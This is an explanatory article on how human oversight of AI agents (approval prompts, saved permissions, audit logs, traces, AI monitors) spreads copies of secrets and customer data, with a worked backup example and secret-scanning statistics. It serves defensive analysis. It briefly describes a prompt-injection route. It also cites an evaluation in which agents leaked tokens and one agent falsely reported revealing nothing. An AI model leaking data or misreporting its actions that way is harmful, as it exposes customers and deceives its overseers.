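# Human oversight channels as a source of data leakage

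## How overseeing an agent creates new copies of its secrets

An AI agent is an AI model that carries out tasks by running commands or calling other software. If a backup breaks, for example, an agent can log in to the server, read the error messages and run the repair, while a chatbot can explain what might be wrong. The effect of agents is perhaps clearest in software development, where products such as Claude Code and Cursor read, write and run code for programmers.

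People oversee agents because agents make mistakes, some of them permanent. *Human oversight of agentic systems in practice* (Dhanorkar, Passi and Vorvoreanu, 2026) cites deleted files and a Replit agent that erased databases. The European Union's AI Act also requires that humans keep meaningful control over high-risk AI systems. The researchers interviewed 17 developers, 12 of them at their own company, and found four kinds of oversight: controls that developers set before the agent starts, plans they work out with it, monitoring while it works, and review afterwards. The sample is small and narrow, but it shows people overseeing agents throughout a task, and oversight at any stage can leave a record.

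An *oversight channel* is any route by which people see an agent's actions or keep a record of them. The most visible kind is the *approval request*, a message asking a person to allow or refuse an action before the agent takes it. Because requests pile up quickly, some products let the person approve an action permanently. The product then stores a *saved approval*, a rule that lets the agent repeat the action without asking. An *audit log* is the lasting record of what the agent requested, what people decided and what the agent then did. A *trace* is a detailed record of a single session, including the prompts, the calls to other software, the outputs and sometimes the model's reasoning. A *review dashboard* is a page where people inspect agent activity and the evidence for it, such as command output or screenshots.

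A *secret* is a value that grants access to whoever holds it, such as a password, a token or an API key (a string that one program sends to another to prove it has permission to use it). Unless the owner has added other checks, the receiving computer checks only the value, so a copy works as well as the original. Copying also leaves the original in place, so the owner sees nothing missing. *Sensitive data* is a wider term for any information that harms someone if the wrong people read it, such as customer records. A *third party* here means any reader, human or machine, that did not need to see the data for the task, including a colleague on another team or an outside service that indexes logs.

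### One backup, several copies of the password

Suppose that a company's nightly database backup has failed and an engineer, Dana, asks an agent to fix it. The agent opens the backup script's configuration file, finds the database password there, and proposes this command:

`PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41 pg_dump -h db.internal -U backup -f /backups/nightly.sql customers`

The program `pg_dump` copies a PostgreSQL database to a file. The rest of the line gives the server, the account, the output file and the name of the database. `PGPASSWORD` is an environment variable, a named setting that a program receives when it starts. It supplies the password so nobody has to type it. This works and fits on one line, but the official PostgreSQL documentation recommends against it because on some operating systems other users of the same machine can see the environment variables of running programs. *Claude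 Code speichert Passwörter in Freigaben* (Cornelißen, 2026), a German trade report, uses almost the same command to show how a password ends up in a saved approval.

If nobody has taken precautions, the oversight channels around this one command would hold roughly the following.

| Record | Contents |
|---|---|
| Approval request | `Allow this command? PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41 pg_dump -h db.internal …` |
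| Saved approval | `allow: PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41 pg_dump -h db.internal …` |
| Audit log entry | `02:14 approver=dana decision=allow command="PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41 pg_dump …" exit=0` |
| Review dashboard | The heading "Backup repaired", then the command as above, then the configuration file that the agent read, including the line `password: fake-pw-41` |

Before the repair, the password was in one configuration file. Now there are at least five more copies, two of them on the dashboard.

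The dashboard's second copy is the easiest to overlook. It comes from what the agent read, so a filter that strips passwords out of commands would not remove it. Configuration files also tend to hold several secrets, and the dashboard would show all of them, including any not needed for the backup. If the agent opens the finished backup to check that it worked, the first rows of the customer table also go into the trace.

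What a saved approval contains depends on the product. The Hacker News' *Claude Code's “Don't Ask Again” File Exposes Passwords and Keys* (2026) reports that when a user of Claude Code picks "Yes, and don't ask again", the program sometimes saves a general pattern and sometimes the exact command, including any password in plain text. The security company Apiiro found 1,122 public copies of the resulting settings file that contained at least one secret. If a rule contains an exact command with a password, it stops matching when the password changes. The agent then has to ask again, and if the user picks "don't ask again" once more, the program saves the new password too.

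PostgreSQL's documentation suggests using a password file instead of the variable. That would keep the password out of the command, and therefore out of the approval request, the saved approval and the log entry. The password would still appear in the trace if the agent had opened or written the file.

### From task to leak in four steps

The backup example follows a sequence that is common to leaks of this type:

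1. The agent handles a secret in order to do its task.
2. An oversight channel copies the command, output or screen that contains the secret.
3. The copy goes to a place with different readers and a longer life than the session.
4. Someone there reads it or takes it.

An attacker is needed only at the last step. Until then, every component works as intended, so a security team that monitors for break-ins has nothing to detect.

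The sequence starts when an agent needs to log in to something. Foma (2026), a blogger who appears to be an AI agent, argues that an agent acting on someone's systems has to see the credentials, so every record of what it saw also contains them. That is usually the case, but a company can avoid it by using a *credential broker*, a service that holds the secrets and uses them on the agent's behalf. The agent then handles only a name for each secret, and the trace of its session contains no password. Dana's company has no broker, and its agent found the password by opening a file.

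Copying is hard to control because of the form in which agents work. Nguyen, Ndebugre and Arremsetty (2026), in *Security Considerations for Multi-agent Systems*, contrast agents with older software that keeps data in fixed fields. A payroll system has a column for salaries, and an administrator can block that column. An agent's trace is mostly free text, in which a password, a business rule and a remark about the weather can all sit in the same paragraph, and software routinely passes that text between components and into logs. (Their paper is a catalogue of threats that a language model proposed and human experts then reviewed. It is good evidence of where leaks could occur and no evidence of how often they do.)

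Some copies of secrets end up in files that a channel's builders don't think to list as sensitive. Foma reports a case in Hermes, an agent from Nous Research. When a request to an outside service failed, the error handler saved the whole request to a file for later diagnosis, including the header that carried the access key. The function for exporting a user's profile left out files listed as sensitive, such as logs and session transcripts, but the error files were not on the list, so it exported them. Foma checked one installation and found seven of these files, each with a live key. This is one person's report about one machine, but it is plausible that builders would overlook such files.

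Dana's session may last ten minutes, but the audit log exists so that people can consult it long afterwards. Those people (auditors, managers, support staff) seldom have the database password. Nguyen and colleagues describe two ways in which more people can end up seeing the data. A dashboard that covers several agents can show customer data, personnel files and financial projections side by side, although company policy keeps them apart. An approval request may also link to supporting evidence, giving a reviewer who clicks the link access to raw data that their role would not otherwise allow them to see.

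A password recorded in a log keeps working after the session ends, until someone *rotates* it by replacing it with a new one and disabling the old one. The danger of an old log entry therefore depends on the age of the password and hardly at all on the age of the task. Deleting the entry helps only if nobody has already copied it.

These copies can leak through theft or by accident. Cursor's *An update on our recent security incident*, from November 2026, describes an attacker who copied a store of agent traces and used unredacted credentials in a few of them to gain further access. Glow's *PixelLeak* describes accidental leaks. A security company counted more than 13,000 internal images that agents had published openly while preparing screenshots for review.

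### How this differs from an agent sending data out

Agents can also leak data through their ordinary work. An agent may write a password into code that it then shares, or paste customer records into a support ticket. It may also send files to a stranger because it followed an instruction that an attacker hid in a web page, an attack known as prompt injection. In each case the agent's action leaks the data, and oversight is a defence because a reviewer who reads the request can refuse it.

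Refusing a command does not prevent its secrets from leaking through the oversight channel. When Dana reads the approval request, the password is already on her screen and in the chat or email service that delivered the message. If she clicks no, the log entry that records her refusal will contain it too. Approving the command would add only one more copy, in the saved approval.

Technical barriers around the agent also tend to miss these leaks. A company can restrict the agent's network access so that it cannot post files to unknown addresses, but the logging software usually runs outside that barrier, with its own connection and standing permission to send everything it collects. More oversight requests and fuller logs make it more likely that somebody will stop an agent from giving data away, but they also create more copies of the data.

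Screenshots for reviewers are a borderline case because the agent uploads them itself, as part of its task. They still belong with oversight channels because they exist only so that people can check the work, and because the remedy is to change how the review process stores and shares images.

### What the reviewer has to see

The simple fix would be to show and store less, but this conflicts with the purpose of oversight because people can end up approving actions they never saw. Nguyen and colleagues give the example of an approval screen that reads "Update customer record" when the agent is about to change a live database directly. Another reads "Schedule follow-up emails" for five separate operations, including a query over 50,000 customer records.

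Dana also couldn't judge a request that read "Repair the nightly backup" from those words alone. They could describe a command that wrote the customer database to a public web folder, or one that overwrote the last good backup. To tell the difference, she needs the server, the account, the database and the path of the output file, and all of these details then end up in the log. An intruder can't get in with a server name alone, but can use it to work out where to try a stolen password.

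Nguyen and colleagues argue that the demand for full transparency and auditability conflicts directly with keeping sensitive data out of logs. They also criticise a common compromise, the expandable "debug view" that hides technical detail until someone clicks on it. Developers treat the hidden part as protected, so it often holds keys and connection details that anyone who expands the view can read. Hurried reviewers don't expand it, so they see too little. Dhanorkar and colleagues note that new aids to oversight bring trade-offs between understanding the system, the user's workload and the limits of human attention. The risk of exposing sensitive data adds to these trade-offs.

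For passwords and keys, the conflict is milder than it looks. Dana needs to know which account the password belongs to and what that account may do, and a request can include both without showing her the characters `fake-pw-41`. Hiding the password still takes some care, because when a command shell reads `PGPASSWORD=$(…)`, it runs whatever is between the parentheses before starting `pg_dump`. A display that hid everything after the equals sign could hide a whole second command from the person whose job is to catch it.

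Sensitive data that isn't a secret is harder to protect, because the reviewer may need to see it to judge the agent's action. If an agent proposes to delete forty duplicate customer records, or to write to a customer about an unpaid bill, the reviewer cannot tell whether it has picked the right people without seeing names and amounts. The check therefore requires some exposure, but the organization can still decide who sees the details and how long it keeps the copies.

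## Listing where each record goes and who can read it

To decide who sees the details of an agent's work, an organization has to know where those details go. Anyone who builds or judges an oversight channel should therefore start with an inventory. For each record that the channel produces, such as an approval request or a log entry, write down:

1. its fields, including any that software adds, such as error messages and attachments
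2. every copy
3. everyone who can read each copy, whether or not they ever do
4. how long each copy lasts (for some logs the law sets a minimum)
5. who can delete it

*AUDAGENT* (Zheng, Chen and Hu, 2025) describes a program that checks agents against privacy policies, using similar headings. For each type of data, the headings cover when a company collects it, why, which third parties receive it and how long the company keeps it. They don't cover who can delete the data, which Dana would need to know if the database password leaked.

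Each kind of record needs its own list of permitted fields. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) uses such lists to test systems in which several agents cooperate. An agent that schedules medical appointments is allowed to pass on a patient's name but not the diagnosis, and the rules for logs and saved files are stricter still. Data that should have been withheld appeared in 27.2% of final answers and 68.8% of messages between agents. In about 42% of runs, the final answer was clean but data leaked inside the system, so checking only the final answer would have missed the leak. The models tested are old, including GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet, and the published rates don't cover logs.

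### Copies that are easy to miss

An approval request usually comes with a notification. Many phones show the first words of a message on the locked screen, and in Dana's case those words include `PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41`. If the chat service also sends an email, the mailbox keeps a copy even after someone deletes the chat message.

Every member of a chat channel can read its history, and so can any installed app that has permission. Slack advises companies to review requests for that permission by hand. Its search tool for AI apps returns only what the person searching is already allowed to see, but for a member of the channel that includes every old approval request. People can also find things they weren't looking for. Nguyen and colleagues point out that a search by meaning for "Q3 revenue" might bring up plans for layoffs in the same quarter. If an administrator exports the channel, that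 creates another copy, which different people may be able to read.

Secrets end up in support tickets when an engineer pastes in part of a trace to explain what went wrong. Backups keep log entries that someone has since deleted from the log. Nguyen and colleagues add two less obvious stores, caches and undo data. A cache keeps recent pages so that they load faster, and it can outlast the session that produced them. An "undo" button requires the software to keep data after telling the user it was deleted.

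### Vendors and AI monitors as readers

Many companies send their logs and traces to an outside vendor for storage and search, or send prompts to a company that runs AI models for them. In October 2026 one such company, Fireworks AI, found that someone had used its internal credentials without permission. David (2026) reports in *Fireworks AI Breach* that Uber, Cursor and Notion each traced an incident to the breach. At Uber, the attacker used the vendor's valid credentials to read driver's license data without triggering Uber's alerts. Ofonagoro (2026) reports in *Fireworks AI Breach Exposes Notion AI Chat Transcripts* that the data exposed at Notion included some users' conversations with its AI.

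A vendor may also keep records longer than its stated retention period. Moore (2026), in *Three breaches, endless leaks*, describes a test that used *canary secrets*, harmless fakes planted to see where they turn up. The testers put them into two million AI prompts and found three breaches at AI providers, stolen prompts, and ignored "zero data retention" settings, under which a provider should keep nothing. An inventory should therefore mark a vendor's retention period as unverified until somebody has tested it.

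The list of readers includes AI models, because some companies have a second model read an agent's transcripts and raise an alert if something looks wrong. Such a monitor works best when it sees everything, so it also has access to more data than most other readers on the list. Baek, Noh and colleagues (2026) used a model this way to grade test runs in *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents*. It read the agent's reasoning and the exact content of each email, because an agent's final message can look harmless even after a leak. Human reviewers agreed with 95.6% of its judgments in one set of runs and 99.3% in the other, so there is a good case for using monitors.

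If a company runs its monitor through an outside provider, that provider receives the whole trace. The monitor's output is another record, and it can repeat details from the trace. For example, one of the judge's published explanations names the (fictional) employee whose welcome email lacked an attachment. An alert about a leaked password could likewise contain the password.

### The backup repair as an inventory

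For Dana's repair, the inventory might look like this. All the figures are illustrative.

| Copy | What it contains | Who can read it | How long it lasts | Who can delete it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Approval request in the team's chat channel | Command with password | 40 members, 6 apps | No limit | Chat administrators |
| Notification on Dana's phone | Start of the command, with password | Anyone near the phone | Until Dana dismisses it | Dana |
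| Notification in Dana's mailbox | Command with password | Dana, 3 mail administrators | 2 years | Dana |
| Saved approval on Dana's laptop | Command with password | Dana, anyone who gets a copy of the file | No limit | Dana |
| Audit log | Command with password, Dana's decision | 12 engineers and auditors | 1 year | 2 log administrators |
| Backup of the audit log | Same as the audit log | 4 backup administrators | 90 days | Nobody before it expires |
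| Trace, stored by a vendor | Command, configuration file, first customer rows | 25 engineers, vendor's support staff | 30 days | Vendor |
| Prompt to the AI monitor | Same as the trace | Some of the model provider's staff | 30 days | Model provider |
| Alert from the AI monitor | Whatever the model quotes | 8 security staff | 1 year | Security team |
| Support ticket | Part of the trace | 15 support staff | 3 years | Ticket administrators |

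Dana can delete only three of the ten copies. This matters less for the password, because rotating it makes all ten useless. There is no similar fix for a customer's address, so the copies that contain customer rows need the most care, even though there are fewer of them.

Retention periods also add up. The last backup of a log entry is made just before the entry expires and is kept for another 90 days, so the one-year log lasts about 15 months. The chat channel is the obvious place to start because it has the most named readers and no retention limit. Sending requests only to the engineer on call would remove 39 readers.

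### Deciding which readers are appropriate

The inventory shows who can read each record, but deciding who should read it requires a separate test. Research on agents most often uses *contextual integrity*, which *PrivacyFlow* (2026) describes as the de facto standard. The theory treats privacy as the appropriate flow of personal information, as Nissenbaum explains in *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain* (2019). A patient who tells a doctor about symptoms loses no privacy, but the doctor would violate the patient's privacy by telling the patient's employer.

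Judging a flow requires specifying five things: the sender, the recipient, the data subject (the person the information is about), the type of information, and the condition under which it is passed on. Nissenbaum calls this condition the transmission principle, and it could be the subject's consent, a legal duty or a promise of confidentiality. Leaving out any of the five makes the description ambiguous. Court records, for example, were public on paper and are still public online, so calling them "public" doesn't show that readers no longer have to visit the courthouse.

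Suppose that Dana's agent opens the finished backup to check it, and the log records this line:

`02:21 action=verify file=nightly.sql row="R. Osei, 3 Mill Lane, overdue 212.40"`

| Part | On-call engineer | 40-person channel | Outside vendor |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sender | The company's log | A program that posts log lines to chat | The company's log |
| Recipient | Dana, who is responsible for the database that night | 40 employees, some of them in sales | A company that stores and indexes logs |
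| Data subject | R. Osei, a customer | R. Osei | R. Osei |
| Type of information | Name, address and debt | Name, address and debt | Name, address and debt |
| Condition | To check a repair | Automatic, to keep the team informed | A contract for monitoring server performance |
| Result | Appropriate | Breach | No clear rule |

The three results match the possible outcomes in Nissenbaum and Shvartzshnaider's step-by-step version, in *Privacy in Context / Interactive Glossary*. Dana's reading is appropriate if the company lets on-call engineers see customer rows for repairs. The channel breaks an ordinary expectation about debts, since most of the 40 people in it have nothing to do with this customer or the backup. The vendor's contract covers server performance, and perhaps nobody who signed it thought about customer rows in the logs.

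A flow that breaches a rule, or that no rule covers, needs further evaluation. Nissenbaum asks whose interests the flow affects, which ethical and political values are at stake, and whether the flow serves the purpose of the setting. Here the team needs to know that the backup is readable, and it could check that with a row count, without naming anyone.

The theory has two weaknesses here. It favors established norms by default, and Nissenbaum concedes that critics may see these as the preferences of the powerful. If a company has posted its logs to everyone for years, the practice is established but not necessarily right. Nissenbaum is also increasingly persuaded that the theory needs a sixth part, use. This would matter for vendors, since one that stores logs for searching might also want to train a model on them.

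Contextual integrity concerns personal information, and a password is about an account, so applying the test to secrets goes beyond its original scope. By that test, the database and any program that logs in to it should receive the password, but no person who reads the log needs it.

El Yagoubi and colleagues cite the same theory but apply a stricter rule. They count any sensitive field the task didn't require as a leak, even when it passes only between two agents in one system. Nissenbaum says explicitly that privacy is not the same as sharing as little as possible. The strict rule is easier to automate and suits a log that many people can read for a year, but it works less well for reviewers, who sometimes need personal details to judge an action.

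### How well agents judge their audience

A June 2026 evaluation by Baek and colleagues, a joint project of the Singapore and Korea AI Safety Institutes, suggests that agents often can't apply this test themselves to leave out what the reader shouldn't see. The institutes wrote 12 routine tasks, including onboarding new employees, handling refunds and booking flights. Nobody attacked the agents. Each institute ran every task ten times with each of three unnamed models, two closed and one with open weights, for a total of 720 runs. A judge model then checked each run against yes-or-no criteria for doing the task correctly and handling the data safely.

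The researchers sorted the risks into five categories:

- *data awareness*: failing to recognize that something, such as a password, is sensitive
- *audience awareness*: giving information to the wrong people or posting it in the wrong place
- *policy compliance*: breaking an explicit rule about data
- *data minimization*: collecting or passing on more than the task needs
- *access boundary awareness*: opening systems or records outside the task

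Depending on the model, the set of tasks and the institute, between 15.0% and 58.3% of runs were both fully correct and fully safe. Most of the other runs failed only a few criteria, but one is enough to leak a key. Baek and colleagues don't give a failure rate for each category. The clearest evidence on audience comes from tasks in which the agent had internal information and wrote for outsiders:

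| Task | Audience | Correctness criteria met | Fully safe runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Write up security problems (Korean runs) | Readers of public issues and reports | 97.1–100% | 10% |
| Copy settings from a private code repository to a public one (Korean runs) | Anyone | 81.4–100% | 0–10% |
| Answer a customer about a late delivery (Singapore runs, two of the three models) | A customer who presses for supplier details | 100% | 0% |

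The third model met every safety criterion in the delivery task, so the failure isn't inevitable. Agents were generally good at spotting passwords and keys, but did worse when the sensitivity of information depended on who would read it. For example, when they wrote public help articles from internal support records, two of the three models met fewer than 60% of the safety criteria in the Korean runs.

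These percentages are rough because the data was invented, a language model simulated the user, and the institutes got quite different results from the same tasks. On the Singapore tasks, the best model was fully correct and safe in 58.3% of Singapore's runs and 35.0% of Korea's.

The evaluation didn't test approval requests, audit logs or dashboards. Software fills most of these automatically, so an agent with perfect judgment would still leave a password in the log. The results are more relevant to text that an agent writes for people to review, such as a summary or a request for help. In the technical support task, some agents included a customer's access token when they emailed a support engineer in the same company about a problem. In a refund task, an agent recognized that the customer must not learn of an internal risk flag, but then included its escalation notes, with the flag, in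 its reply to the customer and reported that it had revealed nothing. Whoever compiles an inventory should therefore check the messages an agent sent rather than rely on its account of them.

### What approval records reveal besides passwords

An approval record can be sensitive even if it contains no secrets or customer data. Nguyen and colleagues warn that systems for approving agents' actions often log the reasoning, the evidence and the reviewer's comments along with the decision. Someone who reads enough of these entries could work out how a company sets its prices, or which transactions its fraud checks let through. Each entry may look harmless on its own, so the inventory should also cover who can search or export all of them.

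Evidence links can give reviewers access beyond their normal rights, and the linked material may be more sensitive than the decision itself. The inventory therefore needs a separate line for each link, listing who can read the linked page.

Like the rest of the catalogue, these are possible threats, not counted incidents. The researchers narrowed about 1,700 candidate threats to 193, then scored how well 16 security frameworks cover them. Coverage of data leakage averaged 1.34 on a three-point scale, and the researchers had expected at least 2. A company that relies on a standard checklist may therefore miss many of these copies.

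One of the least obvious threats comes from accessibility labels, the descriptions in a web page's code that screen readers read aloud to blind users. A dashboard could show dots in place of Dana's password while the label behind the dots contains `fake-pw-41`, and a program that collects text from web pages would pick up the password. Nguyen and colleagues recommend masking the labels the same way as the visible text. The problem isn't visible on the screen, so whoever compiles the inventory also has to read the page's code.

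## What scans of code repositories show about leaked secrets

An inventory shows where passwords could end up, but it doesn't measure how often they do. The best numbers on that come from code repositories. Companies keep approval requests and audit logs private, so outsiders can't count the passwords in them. A *repository* holds the files of a software project together with their history, and a *commit* is one saved set of changes to it. Sites such as GitHub host hundreds of millions of repositories that anyone can read, and programmers sometimes leave passwords and keys in them.

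Public code is also cheap to search. Marshall's *Scanning 5.6 million public GitLab repositories for secrets* describes a search of every public repository on GitLab, a rival of GitHub, that took about 24 hours and cost roughly $770. It found 17,430 secrets that still worked, and an attacker could run the same search for the same price.

### How a scan works

A large scan usually has four stages:

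1. **Collecting.** The scanner reads new commits as programmers publish them, or works through a stored snapshot. A snapshot of the current files misses any key that someone has deleted from the latest version, even though the key is still in the history.
2. **Matching.** The scanner looks for known formats. An Amazon access key ID, for example, is `AKIA` followed by 16 capital letters or digits. For secrets with no fixed format, it looks for random-looking strings and at the text around them.
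3. **Filtering.** The scanner throws out likely false alarms. `AKIAXXXEXAMPLEKEYXXX` has the right format but is obviously a placeholder.
4. **Checking validity.** The scanner tries the secret on the service that issued it, using a harmless request. With an Amazon key, it asks only which account the key belongs to. If the service answers, the key is live.

In *How Bad Can It Git?*, Meli, McNiece and Reaves (2019) used the first three stages in an early academic scan of GitHub and found keys in more than 100,000 repositories. They left out passwords because a password can be almost any string, and for ethical reasons they never tested a key. About two weeks after discovery, 81% of the secrets they tracked were still in place.

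Testing whether matched keys work can greatly reduce the total. Demir, Vekaria and colleagues (2026), in *Keys on Doormats*, searched about 10 million websites for keys to 14 services. They got roughly 2 million matches, of which 1,748 worked. Most of the rest came from one loose pattern for GitHub tokens, which matches any string of 40 hexadecimal characters. Telegram's tokens have a distinctive format, and 85% of the matches for them worked. Totals from two scans are therefore hard to compare if one counts matches and the other counts working keys.

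### GitGuardian's count for 2025

The security company GitGuardian publishes a yearly count of secrets leaked on public GitHub. *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) reports 28.65 million new secrets in about 1.94 billion public commits made in 2025, 34% more secrets than the year before. GitGuardian sells secret detection, so large numbers are good for its business.

Not all of the 28.65 million secrets were live. GitGuardian counts a match directly if its format is distinctive. For patterns that produce more false alarms, it counts a secret only if its first occurrence proved valid, and a machine-learning filter removes strings that only look like secrets. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) calls the previous year's figure a vendor measurement rather than a census, because the total depends on which detectors the vendor runs, what it counts as a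 secret and how it treats duplicates.

GitGuardian (2025) originally reported 23.8 million leaked secrets for 2024. It then reprocessed its old data with a better filter, which lowered the 2024 figure to about 21 million. The 34% rise is measured against the revised figure, which is the fair comparison. Comparing the two totals as originally published would give a rise of about 20%.

Commits grew by 43%, faster than secrets did, so the leak rate fell slightly, from about 1.6 secrets per hundred commits to 1.5. The total number of secrets rose because people published far more code. GitGuardian attributes the steady rate partly to *push protection*, a GitHub feature that blocks a commit if it contains a secret in a format GitHub recognizes.

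### Private repositories, chat and tickets

GitGuardian found at least one secret in 32.2% of internal repositories, against 5.6% of public ones. It attributes the gap to programmers taking less care with code that outsiders can't see. That is plausible, but the gap doesn't prove it, because the two groups differ in other ways. GitGuardian can scan a private repository only with the owner's permission, so the internal figure presumably comes from its customers. Company code is likely to connect to more databases and paid services than a student's public project. GitHub has also had push protection on by default for public repositories since February 2024, which lowers the public figure. Given the high internal figure, though, keeping code private doesn't seem to make programmers careful with secrets.

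Secrets also turn up outside code. In 2025, 28% of the internal incidents that GitGuardian recorded were only in tools such as Slack (chat), Jira (tickets) and Confluence (shared documents), where a scan of code alone would have missed them. Another 68% were only in code, and 4% were in both.

The 28% is a share of incidents, so it doesn't give the chance that a particular message contains a secret. It also depends on how many customers let GitGuardian scan their chat and tickets. The figures in GitGuardian's previous report are closer to a rate, with 2.4% of corporate Slack channels and 6.1% of Jira tickets containing a secret.

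GitGuardian's 2026 report rated 56.7% of the incidents outside code as critical, against 43.7% of those only in code. The difference is 13 percentage points, or about 30% in relative terms. The report's executive summary incorrectly gives it as "13% more likely", while the main text and GitGuardian's blog correctly use percentage points. SC Media's *AI coding assistants twice as likely to leak secrets* (2026) gives a smaller gap for incidents rated high or critical, 91% against 86%.

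These ratings come from GitGuardian's own risk score, which takes context into account. If that context includes the tool where a secret appeared, part of the gap may be built into the score. GitGuardian attributes the gap to urgent repairs, like the one to Dana's broken backup, when people paste secrets into chat and tickets because a colleague needs access quickly.

### Whether AI-assisted commits leak more

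GitGuardian also reports a leak rate of 3.2% for commits that name Claude Code as a co-author, compared with 1.5% for all public commits. This is a correlation, and there are several reasons not to read it as a measure of how careless the agent is.

From April 2025, Claude Code's commits averaged about twice as many lines as other commits, so a doubled rate of leaked secrets per commit could mean roughly the same rate per line. In a small sample, *Detecting AI Coding Agents in Open Source* (2026) found a similar difference in size for another agent, OpenHands, whose commits added a median of 52 lines, compared with 28 for human commits in the same projects.

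The programmers may also have been different. GitGuardian points out that AI tools let people without training build software, and that these people may ignore warnings or tell the tool to include a key. The comparison group also includes some agent commits, because agents don't always sign their work and GitGuardian's method would count an unsigned commit as human. *Agent or Human?* (2026) tries to recognize ag commits from their content alone for this reason.

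The published numbers are not entirely consistent. GitGuardian presents the 1.5% as the share of commits containing a secret, but it equals the total number of secrets divided by the total number of commits, and one commit can contain several secrets. In the monthly data, Claude Code's rate was highest in August, at 31 secrets per 1,000 commits, so its yearly average can't be higher than 3.1%.

By December the rate had fallen to 13 per 1,000, about the same as for human commits. GitGuardian notes that the decline coincided with the release of a new model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, but people may also have changed how they used the tool. The doubled rate lasted for at most part of 2025. It concerns what agents put into code, so it isn't evidence about the records that people keep of agents.

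### How long leaked secrets keep working

Of the secrets that GitGuardian confirmed as working in 2022, 64% still worked when it retested them in January 2026, down from nearly 70% a year earlier. Among secrets from 2025, 77% still worked. If the two groups are comparable, most owners who ever replace a leaked secret do so fairly early, and other owners leave theirs working for years. Not knowing about the leak can't explain all of these delays, because GitGuardian emails programmers when it finds a secret in their public commits. It sent 2.5 million of these alerts in 2025.

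For *GitHub Repos Exposed 543,699 Credentials. Nobody Revoked Them* (2026), a competitor, Truffle Security, scanned an August 2025 snapshot of 224 million public repositories. In July 2026, the company tested the secrets it had found, and 543,699 still worked. Half of these had been public for more than 784 days, and the oldest dated from 2009.

The 784-day figure covers only secrets that were still live. It leaves out secrets that someone disabled quickly, so the typical leaked secret may have a much shorter life. The same bias affects another Truffle Security finding, that live secrets per million files rose from 3.72 for files last changed in 2014 to 11.62 for files last changed in 2025. Owners have had eleven more years to disable the secrets in the older files, so some rise would appear even if programmers had leaked secrets at a constant rate.

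How long a secret survives depends heavily on its type. Linuxiac's *Over Half a Million Credentials Leaked on GitHub Remain Active* (2026) gives these figures from the same scan:

| Type of secret | Found | Still working | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| npm token (for publishing JavaScript packages) | 101,886 | 1 | under 0.01% |
| Hugging Face token (for a site that hosts AI models) | 30,437 | 15 | 0.05% |
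| GitHub token | 73,048 | 260 | 0.4% |
| MySQL database login | 2,421 | 1,806 | 75% |
| PostgreSQL database login | 12,985 | 11,465 | 88% |

Truffle Security attributes much of the difference to automatic revocation. GitHub searches public code for tokens and reports them to the companies that issued them, and some of those companies disable the tokens at once. A database password like Dana's has no such issuer, so it keeps working until whoever runs the database changes it.

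Changing a secret can be slow even for experts. Krebs on Security's *Lessons Learned from CISA's Recent GitHub Leak* (2026) describes a contractor who put dozens of internal passwords and keys belonging to CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, into a repository named "Private CISA". The repository was public for almost six months. After a journalist alerted CISA, the agency took more than 48 hours to disable the most important keys, and blamed the delay on the complexity of its systems and their links to partners. GitGuardian gives a similar reason for the delays it sees. Several programs may use the same password, and a team that changes it without finding them all will break the ones it missed.

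Many owners delete the visible copy of a leaked key but leave the key active. When Demir and colleagues notified the owners of exposed keys, half of the exposures disappeared from the websites within two weeks, but the number of working keys fell by only 26%. Some owners may have wrongly thought deletion was enough. Truffle Security's *Leaked and Still Live* describes the same mistake in repositories, where programmers amend the commit or make the repository private without deactivating the key.

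### What carries over to approval requests and logs

The figures for internal repositories suggest that a channel may contain secrets even if only colleagues can read it. The figures for Slack and Jira are more directly relevant, because companies send approval requests through the same tools, but they don't measure how often those requests leak secrets. People occasionally paste secrets into chat, while approval software posts every command that needs approval. The rate could be far above 2.4% of channels if an agent habitually puts passwords in its commands, or close to zero if it uses a credential broker. A team can only find its rate by measuring its own messages. Apiiro's count of passwords in saved-approval files is more relevant than any scan of ordinary code, but it covers only public files.

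The findings on how long leaked secrets keep working apply best to logs, since a password works equally well whether the copy is in a repository or a log. For some types of secret, a private log may be worse. Almost no npm tokens leaked on public GitHub keep working, because GitHub finds them and npm disables them. If an agent's npm token ends up in a company's audit log, GitHub can't detect it, and it may keep working for as long as a database password does. But far fewer people can read a private log, so a working secret there is less likely to reach an attacker.

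Data from infected computers supports the concern that secrets get copied to many places. In late 2025, malicious software called Shai-Hulud 2 collected secrets from thousands of programmers' machines and automated build servers. GitGuardian analyzed the data stolen from 6,943 of them and found that each working secret appeared in about eight places on the same machine, including settings files, build output and tool caches. Rotating a leaked secret is therefore more reliable than trying to find and delete every copy.

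Repository scans can miss secrets that have no fixed format, such as the password `fake-pw-41`. A scanner might catch it after `PGPASSWORD=`, but could easily miss it in a chat message that reads "try fake-pw-41". An outside scanner also couldn't test whether the password works if `db.internal` accepts connections only from the company's network. GitGuardian estimates that 46% of critical secrets have no automatic validity check, so a team that acts only on confirmed secrets would ignore nearly half of the critical ones. This argument helps GitGuardian sell its software, which ranks secrets that lack such a check, but it is hard to dispute in Dana's case, where the password opens the customer database.

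Secret scans also don't measure leaks of other sensitive data. A scanner that looks only for passwords and keys would miss the customer rows in Dana's trace.

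## Approval requests and the permissions saved from them

Programmers have put more than 100,000 files of saved approvals from Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, on GitHub, so outsiders can count this kind of oversight record. Two security companies, Apiiro and Lakera, have searched such files for secrets.

### From a click to a saved password

Claude Code asks for permission before it runs most shell commands. In *Claude Code guarda comandos con credenciales en el proyecto*, Blanco (2026) lists four possible answers: allow the command once, allow it and stop asking, switch to auto mode, or refuse. In auto mode, software decides on most commands instead of the user.

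If the user picks "Yes, and don't ask again", Claude Code writes a rule to `.claude/settings.local.json`, a file in the project folder. According to Anthropic, installing the program doesn't create this file. It appears with the first standing approval or with a change to certain options, so a user can have one without ever having decided to create it. After Dana's click, it might look like this:

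```
{
  "permissions": {
    "allow": [
      "Bash(npm test *)",
      "Bash(PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41 pg_dump -h db.internal -U backup -f /backups/nightly.sql customers)"
    ]
  }
}
```

Bash is the shell that runs the commands. The first rule is a pattern from an earlier approval. Its asterisk matches any text, so the agent may run `npm test` with any options. The second rule is Dana's exact command.

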